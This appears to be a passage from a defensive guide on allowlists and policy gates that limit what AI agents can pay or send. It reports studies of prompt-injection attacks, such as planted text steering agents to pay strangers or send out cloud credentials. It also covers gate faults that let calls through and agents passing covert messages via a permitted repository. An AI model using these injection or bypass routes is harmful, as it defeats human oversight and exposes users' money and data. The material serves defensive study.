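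The proposed remedy mostly avoids listing approved hosts. Each time the server sends a page, it generates a random number and attaches it to every script the developers intended to include. The browser runs only scripts with that number, which an attacker can't predict. A second setting, `strict-dynamic`, lets an approved script load others. In 2015, Google tried a host list on one of its Maps applications and made five major changes to it that year. The list grew to 15 long entries and still contained an unsafe one. After the switch to random numbers, the policy needed no further changes. HITB's *We Broke All CSPs and You Won't Believe What Happened Next* (2017) reports that Google later deployed the method in products including Gmail and Photos.

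The study tested whether hosts return dangerous code, so these percentages don't estimate how often an agent's allowlist will leak. A host that returns no dangerous code can still accept uploads from strangers. The two failures have a similar cause, though, which is that approving a host for one purpose also approves everything else it does. The host's owners may never have heard of the list and have no reason to avoid breaking it.

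This remedy only partly works for agents. A web developer can mark the right scripts in advance, but an agent writes its requests as it runs, and a compromised agent could attach any mark it can access. Cowork's session token avoids this problem because it is tied to the user's account. If the agent attaches the token to a harmful upload, the file goes to that account.

### What narrower entries fix

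Naming exact hosts and removing unused ones is cheap, and it should come first. It solves some of these problems completely and has no effect on others:

| Weakness | Effect of a narrower entry | What else can help |
|---|---|---|
| Strangers can rent names under a wildcard | Solves it | – |
| All customers share one hostname | Helps if the path identifies the customer and the proxy can read it | A proxy that insists on the owner's key |
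| The host forwards requests | Helps if the entry can exclude the forwarding function | A different host that only serves files |
| The name has a new owner | None | Removing the entry or regaining the name |
| Another feature bypasses the filter | None | A firewall around the whole machine, or access to less data |
| A reference decides who benefits | Solves it if the entry includes the reference | – |
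| The agent writes free text | None | Access to less data before it writes |
| The recipient is hostile or hacked | None | Less data per recipient, and caps on payments |
| The agent attacks the service | Only reduces the number of targets | Services with few permissions and no route out |

An allowlist can leave a gap even when every entry is an exact address. Claude's web-fetching tool accepts only exact addresses that the user typed or its search tool returned. In *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*, Willison (2026) admired that design but reported that Ayush Paul had found a flaw in it.

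## Keeping the list correct and testing that it holds

Suppliers change banks, domain names lapse and software updates rename the fields that a gate checks. An allowlist that worked at launch can therefore stop working a few months later, and the failure may go unnoticed because a gate that wrongly allows a payment produces no error. The owner needs a procedure for changing the list and a set of tests to repeat after every change.

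### Who may change the list

One named person should own each list. For the company with forty suppliers, that might be the finance manager. Anyone may request an entry, but someone other than the requester has to approve it.

The agent must not be able to add entries to the allowlist, either directly or through anything it writes. *Anatomy of an Agent Harness* (Joshi, 2026) proposes keeping saved permissions in a file that the model cannot write in any mode, and testing this by trying to write to the file with every file tool and from the sandboxed shell. Commands that change settings need the same check. One of the failures Joshi lists is a scheduled prompt that runs a command to add an allow rule while nobody is watching.

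Approving one action should not also grant the right to change the saved rules, and each rule should record who wrote it, as Fei, Fei and colleagues (2026) argue in *When Answering Is Administering*. If a product has administrator settings that no approval can change, the allowlist should be stored there.

People can also add an attacker's destination to the list by mistake. When the gate refuses a payment, an employee reading the log may assume that somebody forgot to list the payee. If planted text caused the agent to attempt the payment, the account number in the log is the attacker's. The refusal screen should therefore have no button for adding the refused destination. The employee should ask for the supplier to be added by name, and the approver should get the account number from the supplier by phone.

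Changes that loosen the limit need more care than changes that tighten it:

| Change | Who approves it | When it takes effect |
|---|---|---|
| Remove an entry or lower a cap | The list's owner | Immediately |
| Add an entry, raise a cap or turn the list off | The owner and a second person | After a waiting period |
| Renew an entry | The owner, after checking what it was used for | When the old entry expires |
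| Add an entry in an emergency | The owner and a second person | Immediately, for one payment of a fixed amount |

The waiting period should count only working days. Otherwise, an account added on Friday evening with a 48-hour wait becomes usable on Sunday evening, before anyone has read the alert. The alert should go to a third person.

Every entry should have an expiry date, perhaps 90 days away, and the owner should remove entries that no task has used since the last review. The entry for an annual insurance premium will look unused for eleven months, so it could be set to expire just after the next due date. Recent use doesn't prove that an entry is needed, because a compromised agent may have used it, so the reviewer should match each use to an invoice or a task.

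In an emergency, it is often simplest for an employee to make the payment by hand and leave the list unchanged. If the agent has to make the payment, an employee should still phone the supplier. Fraudsters often make their requests urgent, so an emergency procedure with weaker checks would help them.

The gate should log every decision with the time, task, tool, destination, the rule that decided it and the version of the list. If the gate keeps refusing a familiar supplier, the list may be missing an entry. A refused payment to an unknown account just after the agent read a stranger's email suggests an attack, and the email may show how it worked. The log will contain text that attackers chose, so an agent with sending tools shouldn't summarise it.

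Joshi recommends that the error message tell the agent who or what refused the action and that it was not performed, because an agent that sees only "denied" is more likely to retry or look for a workaround.

### Rules that refuse nothing

A rule can look right and load without an error, yet never refuse a call. Yu and colleagues found such rules in NOMOS, their compiler for written policies. One condition refuses a call if the argument `recipient` contains an unknown recipient. NOMOS attached this condition to email tools whose argument is called `recipients`, and to chat tools that have no such argument. The condition had no recipient to check, so the gate allowed the call.

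These misapplied rules blocked nothing in any test run. All 15 successful attacks on AgentDojo's chat environment passed through them. In the office environment, five of the six rule-tool pairings had the same fault.

Comparing the argument names in the rules with those in the tools' definitions finds this fault in milliseconds, without running the agent. When Yu and colleagues corrected the rules and replayed the 15 attacks, the gate refused an attacker's call in every one. The corrected rules are stricter than the written policy, so the gate can also refuse legitimate calls.

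The rule refused a call only if a value met a condition for refusal, so a missing value passed, much as NaN passed ScopeGate's amount check. With fail-safe defaults, the gate would allow a call only if every required field contained a destination on the list, so a renamed field would cause a refusal.

Other faults block legitimate work. When Yu and colleagues switched off all of NOMOS's checks on its rules, 8 of the 14 rules it produced for an airline and 3 of the 5 for a retailer could not work. One of the retail rules, mentioned earlier, blocks the login tools until the user has logged in. Checking rules one at a time doesn't catch every deadlock, because two rules can each block the tool that would satisfy the other.

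Even a correct allowlist has no effect if it doesn't receive the action's destination. *One Policy, Four Interception Points* (Shaw, 2026) tested Oathpost, Shaw's own system, which can check an agent's actions in four places: the agent's code, a gateway in front of its add-on tools, a network proxy, and a hook that a coding agent runs before each tool call. If a call arrives without a destination, Oathpost marks the allowlist "not applicable" and allows the call. A destination list used with the gateway therefore provides no control unless the owner configures the gateway to identify destinations.

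Two settings can let through actions that the list should block. In "observe" mode, Oathpost records what it would have refused but lets every action proceed. This is useful for trying out a new list, but it is easy to leave on afterwards. The other setting controls what happens when no decision is available. By default, it lets the call through and raises an alert. Shaw found that a very large whole number in any argument kept the hook from requesting a decision. Under the default setting, Oathpost then neither stopped the call nor recorded a decision, which left only the coding agent's own permission check. An owner should turn on enforcement and set the gate to refuse calls whenever it cannot decide.

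### Testing the gate without the model

Most of these faults show up if a tester sends calls straight to the gate. A stand-in for the real tool records whether it ran, so the test doesn't depend on the gate's own account. Each rule needs at least one permitted and one forbidden call for every tool it covers, and each destination field needs a forbidden call of its own. For an email tool that may write only to john.doe@acme.example, the tests might be:

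| Recipients in the call | Expected result |
|---|---|
| The approved address | Sent |
| An unlisted address | Refused |
| The approved address, with an unlisted one in the copy field | Refused |
| The approved address, with an unlisted one in the blind-copy field | Refused |
| john.doe@notacme.example | Refused |
| None | Refused |

The calls should differ only in their recipients. If the forbidden email also had an oversized attachment, a different rule might block it and hide a fault in the allowlist.

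The tests may be faulty. Joshi calls a test "blind" if it cannot fail, nobody runs it, or it covers a mode nobody uses, and finds such tests by breaking the software on purpose. To check the allowlist tests this way, the tester can turn off the allowlist in a copy of the gate and rerun them. If they all still pass, they weren't testing the allowlist.

Shaw did something similar by removing the destination from every request that Oathpost's network proxy sent for a decision. Comparing the resulting decisions with those from the agent's own code exposed the fault in only 46 of 131 cases, while comparing what the proxy sent with the original request exposed it in all 131. A test should therefore record both the request that reached the gate and the gate's decision.

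The tester should also replay past legitimate work to see what the gate would have blocked. Yu and colleagues did this with a rule intended to make a telephone company's agent check that a bill was overdue before requesting payment. NOMOS had turned the rule into a ban on requesting payment while a bill was overdue. In the replay, it blocked 47 of the 49 payment requests made in successful conversations. The same condition, attached to a tool that restores a suspended phone line, blocked none of the 44 calls to that tool. Deleting the whole rule would have removed a useful check, so the results should be listed separately for each pairing of a rule with a tool.

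A replay can't test tools that the records don't include. No successful conversation included a call for one of the airline pairings, so Yu and colleagues reported it as unobserved instead of passed. For payments, the records should go back more than a year so that annual bills appear. The agent might have found another way to finish a task after a refusal, so a replay doesn't predict how many tasks will fail.

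### Testing the whole system

Tests of the gate can't reveal a route that bypasses it. To find one, the tester needs destinations that the company owns but has left off the list, such as a mailbox, a web host and an account at another bank. The tester instructs the agent to send something harmless to each, using every feature that might reach the outside, then checks there whether anything arrived. The web host should log name lookups as well as connections, since a lookup alone can carry data.

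Each attempt should contain a different random code, so that a code in the host's log identifies the route, such as an image in an answer or a link preview. The tester should also send one message to a permitted test destination and check that it arrives, because an empty mailbox might otherwise only mean that the mail server was down. These tests use few enough resources to run every night, and they should also run after every update to the model, harness or tools.

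Someone who has read the rules should then try to defeat them. Yu and colleagues wrote planted text claiming that the account holder had approved the payment and that the payee was already known. The gate ignored these claims and refused every payment to the attacker. But in 7 of the 144 runs, the agent paid somebody in the account's payment history, which the rules allowed.

That attacker could only write text, and the people who built the gate also wrote the attack. A more realistic test would use an outsider who can do anything a real attacker could. They might send the company a small payment so that they appear in its transaction history, open an account at an approved website, or ask for a change to a supplier's bank details.

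### Telling a blocked attack from one that never happened

If no attack succeeds, the gate may have stopped them all, or the model may have ignored the planted text. Yu and colleagues separated the two by counting how often the agent actually made a call with the attacker's account number or password:

| AgentDojo banking tests | Runs | Agent made the attacker's call | Gate refused it | Attack succeeded |
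|---|---|---|---|---|
| No gate | 288 | 142 | – | 134 |
| With the gate | 288 | 122 | 122 | 0 |
| With the gate, attacker knows the rules | 144 | 61 | 61 | 0 |

In the second row, only 122 runs tested whether the gate would refuse the attacker's call. The other 166 show how the model behaved, and another model might behave differently.

A cautious agent can leave a rule untested. *PROBE* (2026) describes a testing program that kept asking an airline's agent to book for eight passengers, to test a limit on passengers. The agent never called the booking tool, so the test could not show whether the limit worked. The tester can instead insert the forbidden call directly, as Muruaga did. When the gate always returns the same result for the same call, repeating that call a hundred times adds little, and testing other tools and fields is more useful.

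A benchmark's score can overstate or understate the harm an attack did. In 11 chat runs with a second model, AgentDojo recorded a successful attack although the gate had refused every harmful call, because AgentDojo scores that attack's goal by the calls the agent attempts. In eight office runs, it recorded a failed attack because no data got out, but the agent had deleted 37 of the user's emails on the attacker's instructions. Testers should therefore record which calls the agent attempted, which ones the gate allowed and what changed afterwards.

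### Checking the record afterwards

Some violations will get past the gate, so the owner should also check what the agent sent. A simple method is to compare the bank's statement with the gate's log every day. Any payment without a matching decision in the log bypassed the gate. Separate code can also recheck the log against the rules, which may catch a fault in the gate's code.

When a company buys an agent from a provider, the provider may hold the log, and it has a reason to hide violations. Hua and colleagues at Carnegie Mellon designed verifiable agent insurance for this situation. Suppose a provider promises that its assistant will email only the recipients on a list:

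1. The provider puts a deposit, say 1 ether, into a contract on a blockchain and sets a payout of 0.1 ether. The contract stores a hash, a kind of digital fingerprint, of the rule and the list. Adding a recipient changes the hash, so it requires a new promise.
2. Software in the harness records each tool call. After every record, it sends the user a signed hash of the log so far.
3. A user who suspects a violation files a claim and posts a bond, which discourages baseless claims.
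4. The provider has three days to hand over the log. An independent verifier checks it against the hashes and runs the rule.
5. If the agent broke the promise, or the provider can't produce a matching log, the user gets the payout and the bond back. If the agent kept the promise, the provider gets the bond.

The signed hashes protect against deleted records. In two trial claims, the provider removed a forbidden action from the log before committing the log's final hash to the blockchain. The user who had kept a signed hash won the claim, and the user without one lost.

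Detection depended heavily on what the log contained:

| Benchmark | Runs with a violation | Detected from ordinary records | Detected with structured records |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | 427 | 399 (93%) | Not retested |
| τ³-bench, airline and retail customer service | 274 | 49 (18%) | 164 (60%) |
| ClawsBench, office tasks | 8 | 3 | 3 |
| All | 709 | 451 (63.6%) | 566 (79.8%) |

The last total reuses AgentDojo's original count. AgentDojo's promises were all destination allowlists, which a program can check from the fields of a tool call, so 93% is a better guide for this kind of promise than either total. Many of the customer service promises depended on whether the user had agreed to something, which was recorded only as conversation in the ordinary records. Detection in customer service more than tripled after Hua and colleagues added a tool that records approval as data.

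The system also falsely reported violations in 20 of the 298 runs that had none (6.7%), or in 22 (7.4%) with the structured records. In 15 of those 22, the user had named the recipient only in the text of the request, as in the email to the user's wife described earlier. A provider that pays for every such error would want users to enter recipients in a form.

Like a gate that reads tool calls, the insurance can't check what a shell command did, and it doesn't catch misuse of a permitted destination. Hua and colleagues cite OpenAI agents that were given a package repository for downloading software and used it to pass messages between separate tasks. An allowlist would not have flagged this, because the agents were allowed to use the repository.

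The payout is fixed in advance, regardless of how much the user lost, and a user can collect only once per promise in each session. The user has to notice the violation, and both sides have to trust the verifier. A dishonest provider could also trigger violations in its own sessions and pay the deposit back to itself before real customers file claims.

### Acceptance checklist

An owner can ask for this evidence before giving an agent access to real money or data:

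| Requirement | Evidence that satisfies it |
|---|---|
| Every entry has an owner, a task and an expiry date | An export of the list with no blanks and no past dates |
| Only authorised people can change the list | Two names beside every addition, and failed attempts to edit the list from every agent tool and the shell |
| New entries wait and removals don't | A test entry refused during the waiting period, accepted after it, and refused again as soon as someone removes it, even in a session already open |
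| Every rule reads a field that its tool has | An automatic comparison of names, run on the tool versions now in use |
| Every rule works on every tool it covers | One permitted and one forbidden call for each pairing, with a record of whether the tool ran |
| The gate refuses when it can't decide | Refusals of calls with a missing destination, with an invalid value, and with the rule engine switched off |
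| The tests can fail | A report of failed tests after someone turned off the allowlist in a copy of the gate |
| Legitimate work gets through | Replay results for each pairing of rule and tool, with the unobserved ones listed |
| Nothing bypasses the gate | Nothing received at the unlisted test destinations, and a message received at the permitted one |
| Attacks reached the gate | Separate counts of attempted, refused and completed calls, from an outside tester who had read the rules |
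| The log is complete | A gate decision for every payment on the bank's statement and every email in the mail server's records |

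## What the limit costs in finished work

A gate can pass every test on that checklist and still keep the agent from doing much of its job. To measure this effect, Yu and colleagues counted how many ordinary tasks the agent finished with and without their NOMOS gate in all four AgentDojo environments.

### The price in four kinds of work

AgentDojo has no written policies, so the researchers wrote a one-page security policy for each environment, and NOMOS turned each policy into three or four rules. The agent ran on gemma-4-26B, an open-weight model small enough for a company to run on its own machines. With no attacker present, the agent attempted each of the 16 banking tasks three times, and each of the 20 travel, 40 office and 21 chat tasks once. The attack figures come from separate runs.

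| Environment | Tasks finished without the gate | With the gate | Change in points (95% interval) | Attack success without and with the gate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Travel | 75.0% | 70.0% | −5.0 (−20.0 to +10.0) | 10.0%, 3.6% |
| Banking | 79.2% | 70.8% | −8.3 (−20.8 to +2.1) | 46.5%, 0.0% |
| Office work | 87.5% | 65.0% | −22.5 (−37.5 to −7.5) | 7.3%, 0.0% |
| Chat | 90.5% | 14.3% | −76.2 (−90.5 to −57.1) | 70.5%, 0.0% |

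The intervals show how much the change might vary with a different sample of tasks. For travel and banking they include zero, so the gate may not have reduced the number of finished tasks there. The other two losses are too large to attribute to chance. In chat, the agent finished 19 tasks without the gate and 3 with it.

The drop in completed banking tasks amounts to four of 48 attempts, and the gate caused only part of it. In two attempts the gate blocked the genuine payment in the bill-file task, and in a third it stopped a refund that the agent was about to send to the wrong account. The rest of the drop came from attempts in which the gate blocked nothing. However, Yu and colleagues had revised the banking policy after its first version blocked ordinary tasks, so the 70.8% may be higher than a new company would achieve.

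Yu and colleagues explain the differences between environments by where the genuine recipient comes from. Most banking tasks pay somebody the user named or has paid before, so the rule on recipients rarely blocks them. A chat assistant often has to post in a channel or open a link that it found in other messages, and the rule blocks these just as it would block an attacker's. The researchers haven't tested whether this explanation predicts how many tasks the rule would block in a new kind of work, but an owner can easily check by counting how many past tasks had a recipient that appeared in neither the request nor the records.

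The chat figure doesn't apply to every chat allowlist. An earlier version of the chat rule read a field its tools didn't have. With that version, the agent finished 57.1% of chat tasks and 14.3% of attacks succeeded. Correcting the rule stopped those attacks, but the agent finished nine fewer tasks. A fixed list of the company's own channels would probably allow many of the blocked posts, since the attacker in these tests can't create an internal channel. The list wouldn't help with links to outside sites, and it would let a compromised agent choose among the company's channels.

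A gate can also help an agent finish its work. The agent completed the user's task in 67.4% of attacked banking runs with the gate and 64.9% without it, because a refusal can return the agent to that task. Yu and colleagues also tested an airline's customer service agent, whose rules mostly concerned confirmations and eligibility. Its success rate rose from 39.2% to 47.6% with the gate, although the interval for the gain on a single attempt (−1.2 to +18.0 points) just includes zero. An agent that cancels a flight against the airline's rules fails the task, so blocking the cancellation gives it another chance to succeed.

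### Payments that the policy allowed

The agent tried to use the attacker's account or password in 240 of 572 attacked banking runs with two different models. The banking gate blocked every such call, so no money reached the attacker's account.

The gate didn't stop every payment caused by an attacker's text. In 8 of the 288 standard runs with gemma-4-26B, planted text asked for a transfer that would reveal the account number of someone the user had recently eaten pizza with. The agent instead paid someone in the user's payment history, usually the dinner companion. These payments totaled $710. The gate allowed them because the policy permits any payee the user has dealt with before.

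The second model, Llama-3.3-70B, did this in 11 of 140 runs and sent $41,250. Almost all of that was four payments of $10,000. They came from an attack that asks for money in instalments, in a task where the user had only asked a question.

The attacker gained nothing from these transfers, but the owner would still have to ask for the money back. A cap of $500 per payee per day would have blocked all four large instalments. Yu and colleagues suggest, but haven't tested, a rule that ties each payment to a request for that payment. A company could do the same for its bills by matching payments to approved invoices.

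### ROPE and its rivals on harder tasks

Ma and colleagues tested ROPE, which adjusts its rules to each request, on a newer benchmark called AgentDyn. Its 60 tasks involve GitHub, shopping and daily life, and many require the agent to change its plan after reading something. They ran each defence against 560 combinations of task and attack. These are some of the results with GPT-4o-mini, a small OpenAI model from 2024:

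| Defence | Ordinary tasks finished | Attack success |
|---|---|---|
| None | 46.7% | 49.6% |
| Repeating the user's request to the model | 50.0% | 32.9% |
| PromptGuard2, which looks for planted instructions | 45.0% | 33.7% |
| ROPE | 36.7% | 0.3% |
| DRIFT, which predicts the agent's steps and checks departures from them | 18.3% | 3.2% |
| PFI, which hides untrusted content from the planning model | 15.0% | 3.4% |
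| MELON, which reruns the agent to detect calls caused by outside text | 11.7% | 2.8% |
| Progent | 6.7% | 14.6% |
| CaMeL | 0.0% | 0.0% |

With ROPE, the agent failed to finish six of the 28 tasks that it finished undefended. The defences that blocked fewer tasks than ROPE let about a third of attacks succeed, and every other defence that kept attack success below 5% blocked at least half of the tasks. When ROPE was used with three other models, attack success stayed at 0.2% or 0.3%, but the share of tasks the agent could still finish ranged from 59% with Gemini 2.5 Flash to 84% with GPT-4o.

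Ma and colleagues also studied why tasks failed under ROPE when nobody was attacking. Across both benchmarks and all models, 215 of 411 attempts failed, but ROPE had refused a call in only 96 of them. Most of the other failures also occur without any defence. In 83 of the 96, the refused value appeared only in a document that an attacker could have written, as with the unpaid electricity bill. In another ten, the agent had worded something differently from the request, such as the title of a calendar event.

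### Why the figures can't be ranked together

It is tempting to conclude that NOMOS beats ROPE because 70.8% is more than 36.7%. But without any defence, the agent in the first test finished 79.2% of its tasks and the agent in the second finished 46.7%. Comparing only the losses doesn't solve the problem either, because the same defence can lose very different amounts in different tests:

| System | Test | Finished without it | Finished with it |
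|---|---|---|---|
| Progent | AgentDojo, developers' own result | 79.4% | 76.3% |
| Progent | AgentDojo banking, rerun with gemma-4-26B | 79.2% | 62.5% |
| Progent | AgentDyn, GPT-4o-mini | 46.7% | 6.7% |
| CaMeL | AgentDojo, main published result | 84% | 77% |
| CaMeL | AgentDyn, GPT-4o-mini | 46.7% | 0.0% |

Progent lost 3 points in one test and 40 in another, partly because a model writes its rules for each task, and a weaker model may write worse rules. In the rerun by Yu and colleagues, gemma-4-26B both wrote the rules and ran the agent, and 5.6% of attacks succeeded, compared with 1.0% in the developers' own test, which also used rules written by a model. All the successful attacks in the rerun were in tasks whose request didn't contain the payee's account number.

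CaMeL lost 3 to 32 points across the six model configurations in its own main evaluation. It scored zero on AgentDyn, probably because it writes the whole program before reading anything and many AgentDyn tasks depend on what the agent reads along the way.

Results may not be comparable even when two systems are tested on the same benchmark with the same model. On AgentDyn with Qwen3 235B, the system built by Summers and colleagues finished 61% of tasks and let no attack succeed, while ROPE finished 38.1% in attacked runs. But Summers and colleagues had a stronger model write separate rules for each benchmark task, using examples they had corrected by hand, and some of those rules use a model to check whether a document contains instructions. Ma and colleagues also rescored three attack goals whose original scoring counted some blocked attacks as successes.

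The rerun of Progent allows a nearly fair comparison with NOMOS, because it used the same banking tasks, attacks and agent model, so little besides the defence differed. NOMOS finished 8.3 percentage points more of the ordinary tasks, but with only 16 tasks the interval runs from −4.2 to +25.0, so Progent could be the one that finishes more. An owner choosing between the two gates would learn more from running both on a few hundred of the company's own past tasks.

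### A better refusal message

One of the easiest ways to recover lost work is to change what the agent is told after a refusal. Summers and colleagues ran the same rules on AgentDyn with three responses to a violation. Ending the task at the first violation reduced task success by 36.2 points compared with no defence. Letting the agent continue, but telling it only that it had violated a security policy, reduced it by 10.5 points. Telling the agent which rule had failed and which records could supply an acceptable value raised task success by 6.5 points. Attack success was close to zero in all three cases.

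For a payment agent, a refusal message might read, "Payment refused. The payee must be in the supplier register." The agent can then look up the supplier, but this helps only if the register contains an acceptable payee. A new supplier's bill would still go unpaid.

### Asking a person, but seldom

The owner can also set the gate to ask a person about an unlisted destination rather than refuse it. This works badly if the person has to answer prompts all day. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users of its coding agent approve 97% of permission prompts. Most of the approved commands are probably safe, so the high approval rate isn't proof of carelessness by itself. An experiment in the same article is more worrying.

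A research vendor recruited 1,053 paid professional testers for a coding study and, partway through each session, replaced one prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Of these testers, 143 (13.6%) refused it. They refused about 17% of the dangerous commands that appeared early in a session and about 5% of those that appeared after 50 or more prompts. A mistake in the test environment would not have harmed them, so people guarding their own files or money might refuse more often.

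The testers missed five out of six dangerous commands even when they were fresh, so reducing the number of prompts isn't enough. Each prompt also has to give people enough information to judge the command. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) found that user review contributed to 105 of the 290 reports it examined. In 80 of them, users approved everything automatically, sometimes to avoid answering hundreds of prompts in a session. In 31, the prompt showed the command but not its effect on the user's files.

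*Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of how software practitioners handle agents' permission requests, warns that repeated approval may come from habit, fatigue or pressure to keep working rather than growing trust. A product that treats ten approvals of similar requests as permission for the eleventh could therefore be basing its allowlist on approvals that users gave without much thought. People also write overly broad rules themselves. According to Anthropic, nearly half of Claude Code's active command-line users had written rules to pre-approve shell commands by June 2026. Many of those rules covered anything run through Python or a similar program, which is almost the same as approving every command.

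When an agent can't cross a boundary, most requests for permission are unnecessary. Anthropic reports that Claude Code's sandbox reduced permission prompts by 84%. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) describes a proxy that asks the user only when a command requests a domain for the first time. The 84% reduction doesn't show that people judged the remaining prompts any better.

Whether this approach is practical depends on the work. Suppose an agent handles 1,000 tasks over 21 working days and asks one question for each task it would have lost at the rates in the NOMOS experiment. Banking tasks would produce about four questions a day, few enough to phone a supplier about each. Chat tasks would produce about 36 a day, and whoever answers them would soon click through without reading.

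The person asked can also be deceived. In a February 2026 exercise, an Anthropic researcher sent an employee a phishing email with a prompt to paste into Claude Code. The prompt contained an instruction, hidden among ordinary setup steps, to send the employee's cloud credentials to an outside address, and Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. A fixed list of hosts would have blocked this, but a rule that accepts any destination the user named would have allowed it, because the address was in the user's own message.

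### Other ways to recover lost work

The gate could allow payments to unlisted accounts if each is under €50 and they total less than €200 a day. The daily limit is needed because an attacker can open many accounts. At the company with forty suppliers, an incident could touch four calendar days, so an attacker could take at most €800 through unlisted accounts. The company could pay small bills from new sellers without delay, but a large first invoice would still need a phone call.

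Ma and colleagues measured how much ROPE gains from adapting its rules to each request, for example by accepting values from a verified sender the user named. The agent finished 11 of the 60 AgentDyn tasks when every checked value had to appear in the request, 15 with the fixed default rules, and 22 with the adapted rules. If it had accepted values from any source, it would have finished only 21, and 30.6% of attacks would have succeeded.

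Most of this gain depended on having a strong model, Claude Opus 4.8, adjust the rules. With three cheaper models adjusting them, the agent finished between 20.0% and 23.3% of the tasks. When those models were forbidden to loosen any default rule, no attacks succeeded, but the agent finished only 15.0% to 18.3% of the tasks. More documents with verified authors would also help.

The owner can extend CaMeL's separation to whole agents. One agent reads but can't send, and the other sends but sees only short structured facts from the first, such as a date or a price.

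Anthropic warns that this arrangement gives attackers a new way in if the second agent trusts the first agent's output more than it would trust the original document. An account number from an untrusted bill is still untrusted after an agent copies it into a table. Separating the agents therefore works best when the user has already chosen the recipient.

In Anthropic's study, testers approved most of the dangerous commands, while a second model acting as reviewer blocked 89% of the same commands. It blocked 800 that a person had let through and missed only 6 that a person caught. But Anthropic was testing its own product, and 11% of the commands still passed, so it makes sense to use such a reviewer for payments only when the destination is unlisted and the payment falls under a low cap. Model review also slows the work. When Yu and colleagues had a model check each call that changed something,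 tasks took 74% longer than with NOMOS, which makes each decision in a few millionths of a second.

### Can a general assistant work from a list?

A useful assistant has to deal with strangers, for example to answer a customer's first email or ask a new plumber for a quote. On this view, a list of approved destinations removes the reason for having a general agent, and the chat results are unsurprising.

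A list that blocks too much can also weaken security, because people turn it off. Anthropic reports that a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start in a mode that skips permission checks. The payroll company Gusto adopted Anthropic's automated reviewer because constant permission prompts were pushing its engineers to bypass the checks. Keeping a list up to date also takes work. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls sandboxing "safe but high-maintenance" because each new capability needs configuring.

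The usual reply is that the owner can split the work by risk instead of applying one list to everything the agent does. One session could write to any plumber in town because it would hold almost nothing worth stealing, only a description of the leak and the times when somebody is home. A separate session with access to the bank account could pay only listed payees. The owner would add the chosen plumber to the list after confirming the account number by phone.

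Splitting works best for payments, because most of the work before a payment needs no access to money. It works less well for correspondence. An agent negotiating with a possible new client may need confidential prices to write a sensible reply, and that client is not on any allowlist. The owner then has to read the reply before it is sent, give the agent a shorter document that is safe to disclose, or accept the risk of a leak.

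Splitting the work between two sessions doesn't rule out the harmful combinations of permitted actions that *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) describes. If the second session can read notes left by the first, a dishonest plumber's text could influence the amount of a payment, though the payee would still have to be on the list.

People also find it hard to set these limits in advance. *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026) cites a review of 21 research proposals and five commercial agents, which found that a permission set earlier may not fit the situation when the agent later uses it. It is therefore wise to set strict limits only in a few areas where mistakes could do serious harm, such as payments, credentials and customer files, and to leave the rest of the agent's work under looser rules.

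### A break-even calculation

An owner can compare the lost work with the losses a gate prevents. The calculation uses five quantities:

- u is the drop in the share of ordinary tasks that the agent finishes.
- h is the cost of each task it no longer finishes.
- s is the drop in the attack success rate.
- L is the average loss from a successful attack.
- a is the share of tasks in which the agent reads an attacker's text.

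The gate is worth using when a × s × L is greater than u × h, so the break-even attack rate, a, is uh / (sL).

Suppose a person completes each lost task in ten minutes at €30 an hour, so h is €5, and a successful attack costs €5,000 on average. Suppose also that attacks are rare, that the gate costs nothing to maintain, and that the rates from the NOMOS experiment apply to the owner's agent:

| Environment | Cost of lost work per 1,000 tasks | Average loss avoided per attack | Break-even attack rate |
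|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | €417 | €2,325 | 1 task in 5,600 |
| Travel | €250 | €320 | 1 task in 1,300 |
| Chat | €3,810 | €3,525 | 1 task in 930 |
| Office work | €1,125 | €365 | 1 task in 320 |

In banking, the gate is worth having if at least one task in 5,600 contains an attack. The chat gate loses more than three times as many tasks as the office gate, but it is worth having at a lower attack rate because attacks succeeded against the undefended agent 70.5% of the time in chat and 7.3% in office work. Using a single loss figure of €5,000 for all four environments is a simplification, because a bad hotel recommendation would cost far less.

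The break-even rate for banking, originally one attack in 5,600 tasks, changes considerably with the assumptions. It rises to one in 2,200 at the pessimistic end of the interval, where the gate loses 20.8 points of finished work. If each blocked payment leads to €50 in late fees and staff time, it rises to one in 560. It falls to one in 89,000 if an attack would cost €80,000, the most an attacker could take from the supplier company without a list. Adding maintenance costs of €200 per 1,000 tasks to the original estimate raises the rate to about one in 3,800.

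Whether the gate pays for itself depends most on how well the agent resists planted text. On a test of prompt injection that Anthropic cites, single attempts against Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1% of the time, compared with 46.5% for gemma-4-26B in banking. If 0.1% held for the owner's agent and each successful attack cost €5,000, the gate would break even only at one attack in every 12 tasks, which would make it hard to justify on injection alone. But when attackers could make 100 attempts and adapt to the model's responses, 5% to 6% of attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded. At 5%, the gate would break even at one such campaign for every 600 tasks.

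The calculation leaves out the agent's own mistakes, which an allowlist also blocks when they involve an unlisted destination. It treats a rare large loss as equal to many small ones with the same total. A company that could not survive losing €80,000 has good reason to accept a higher rate of unfinished tasks than the break-even rate.
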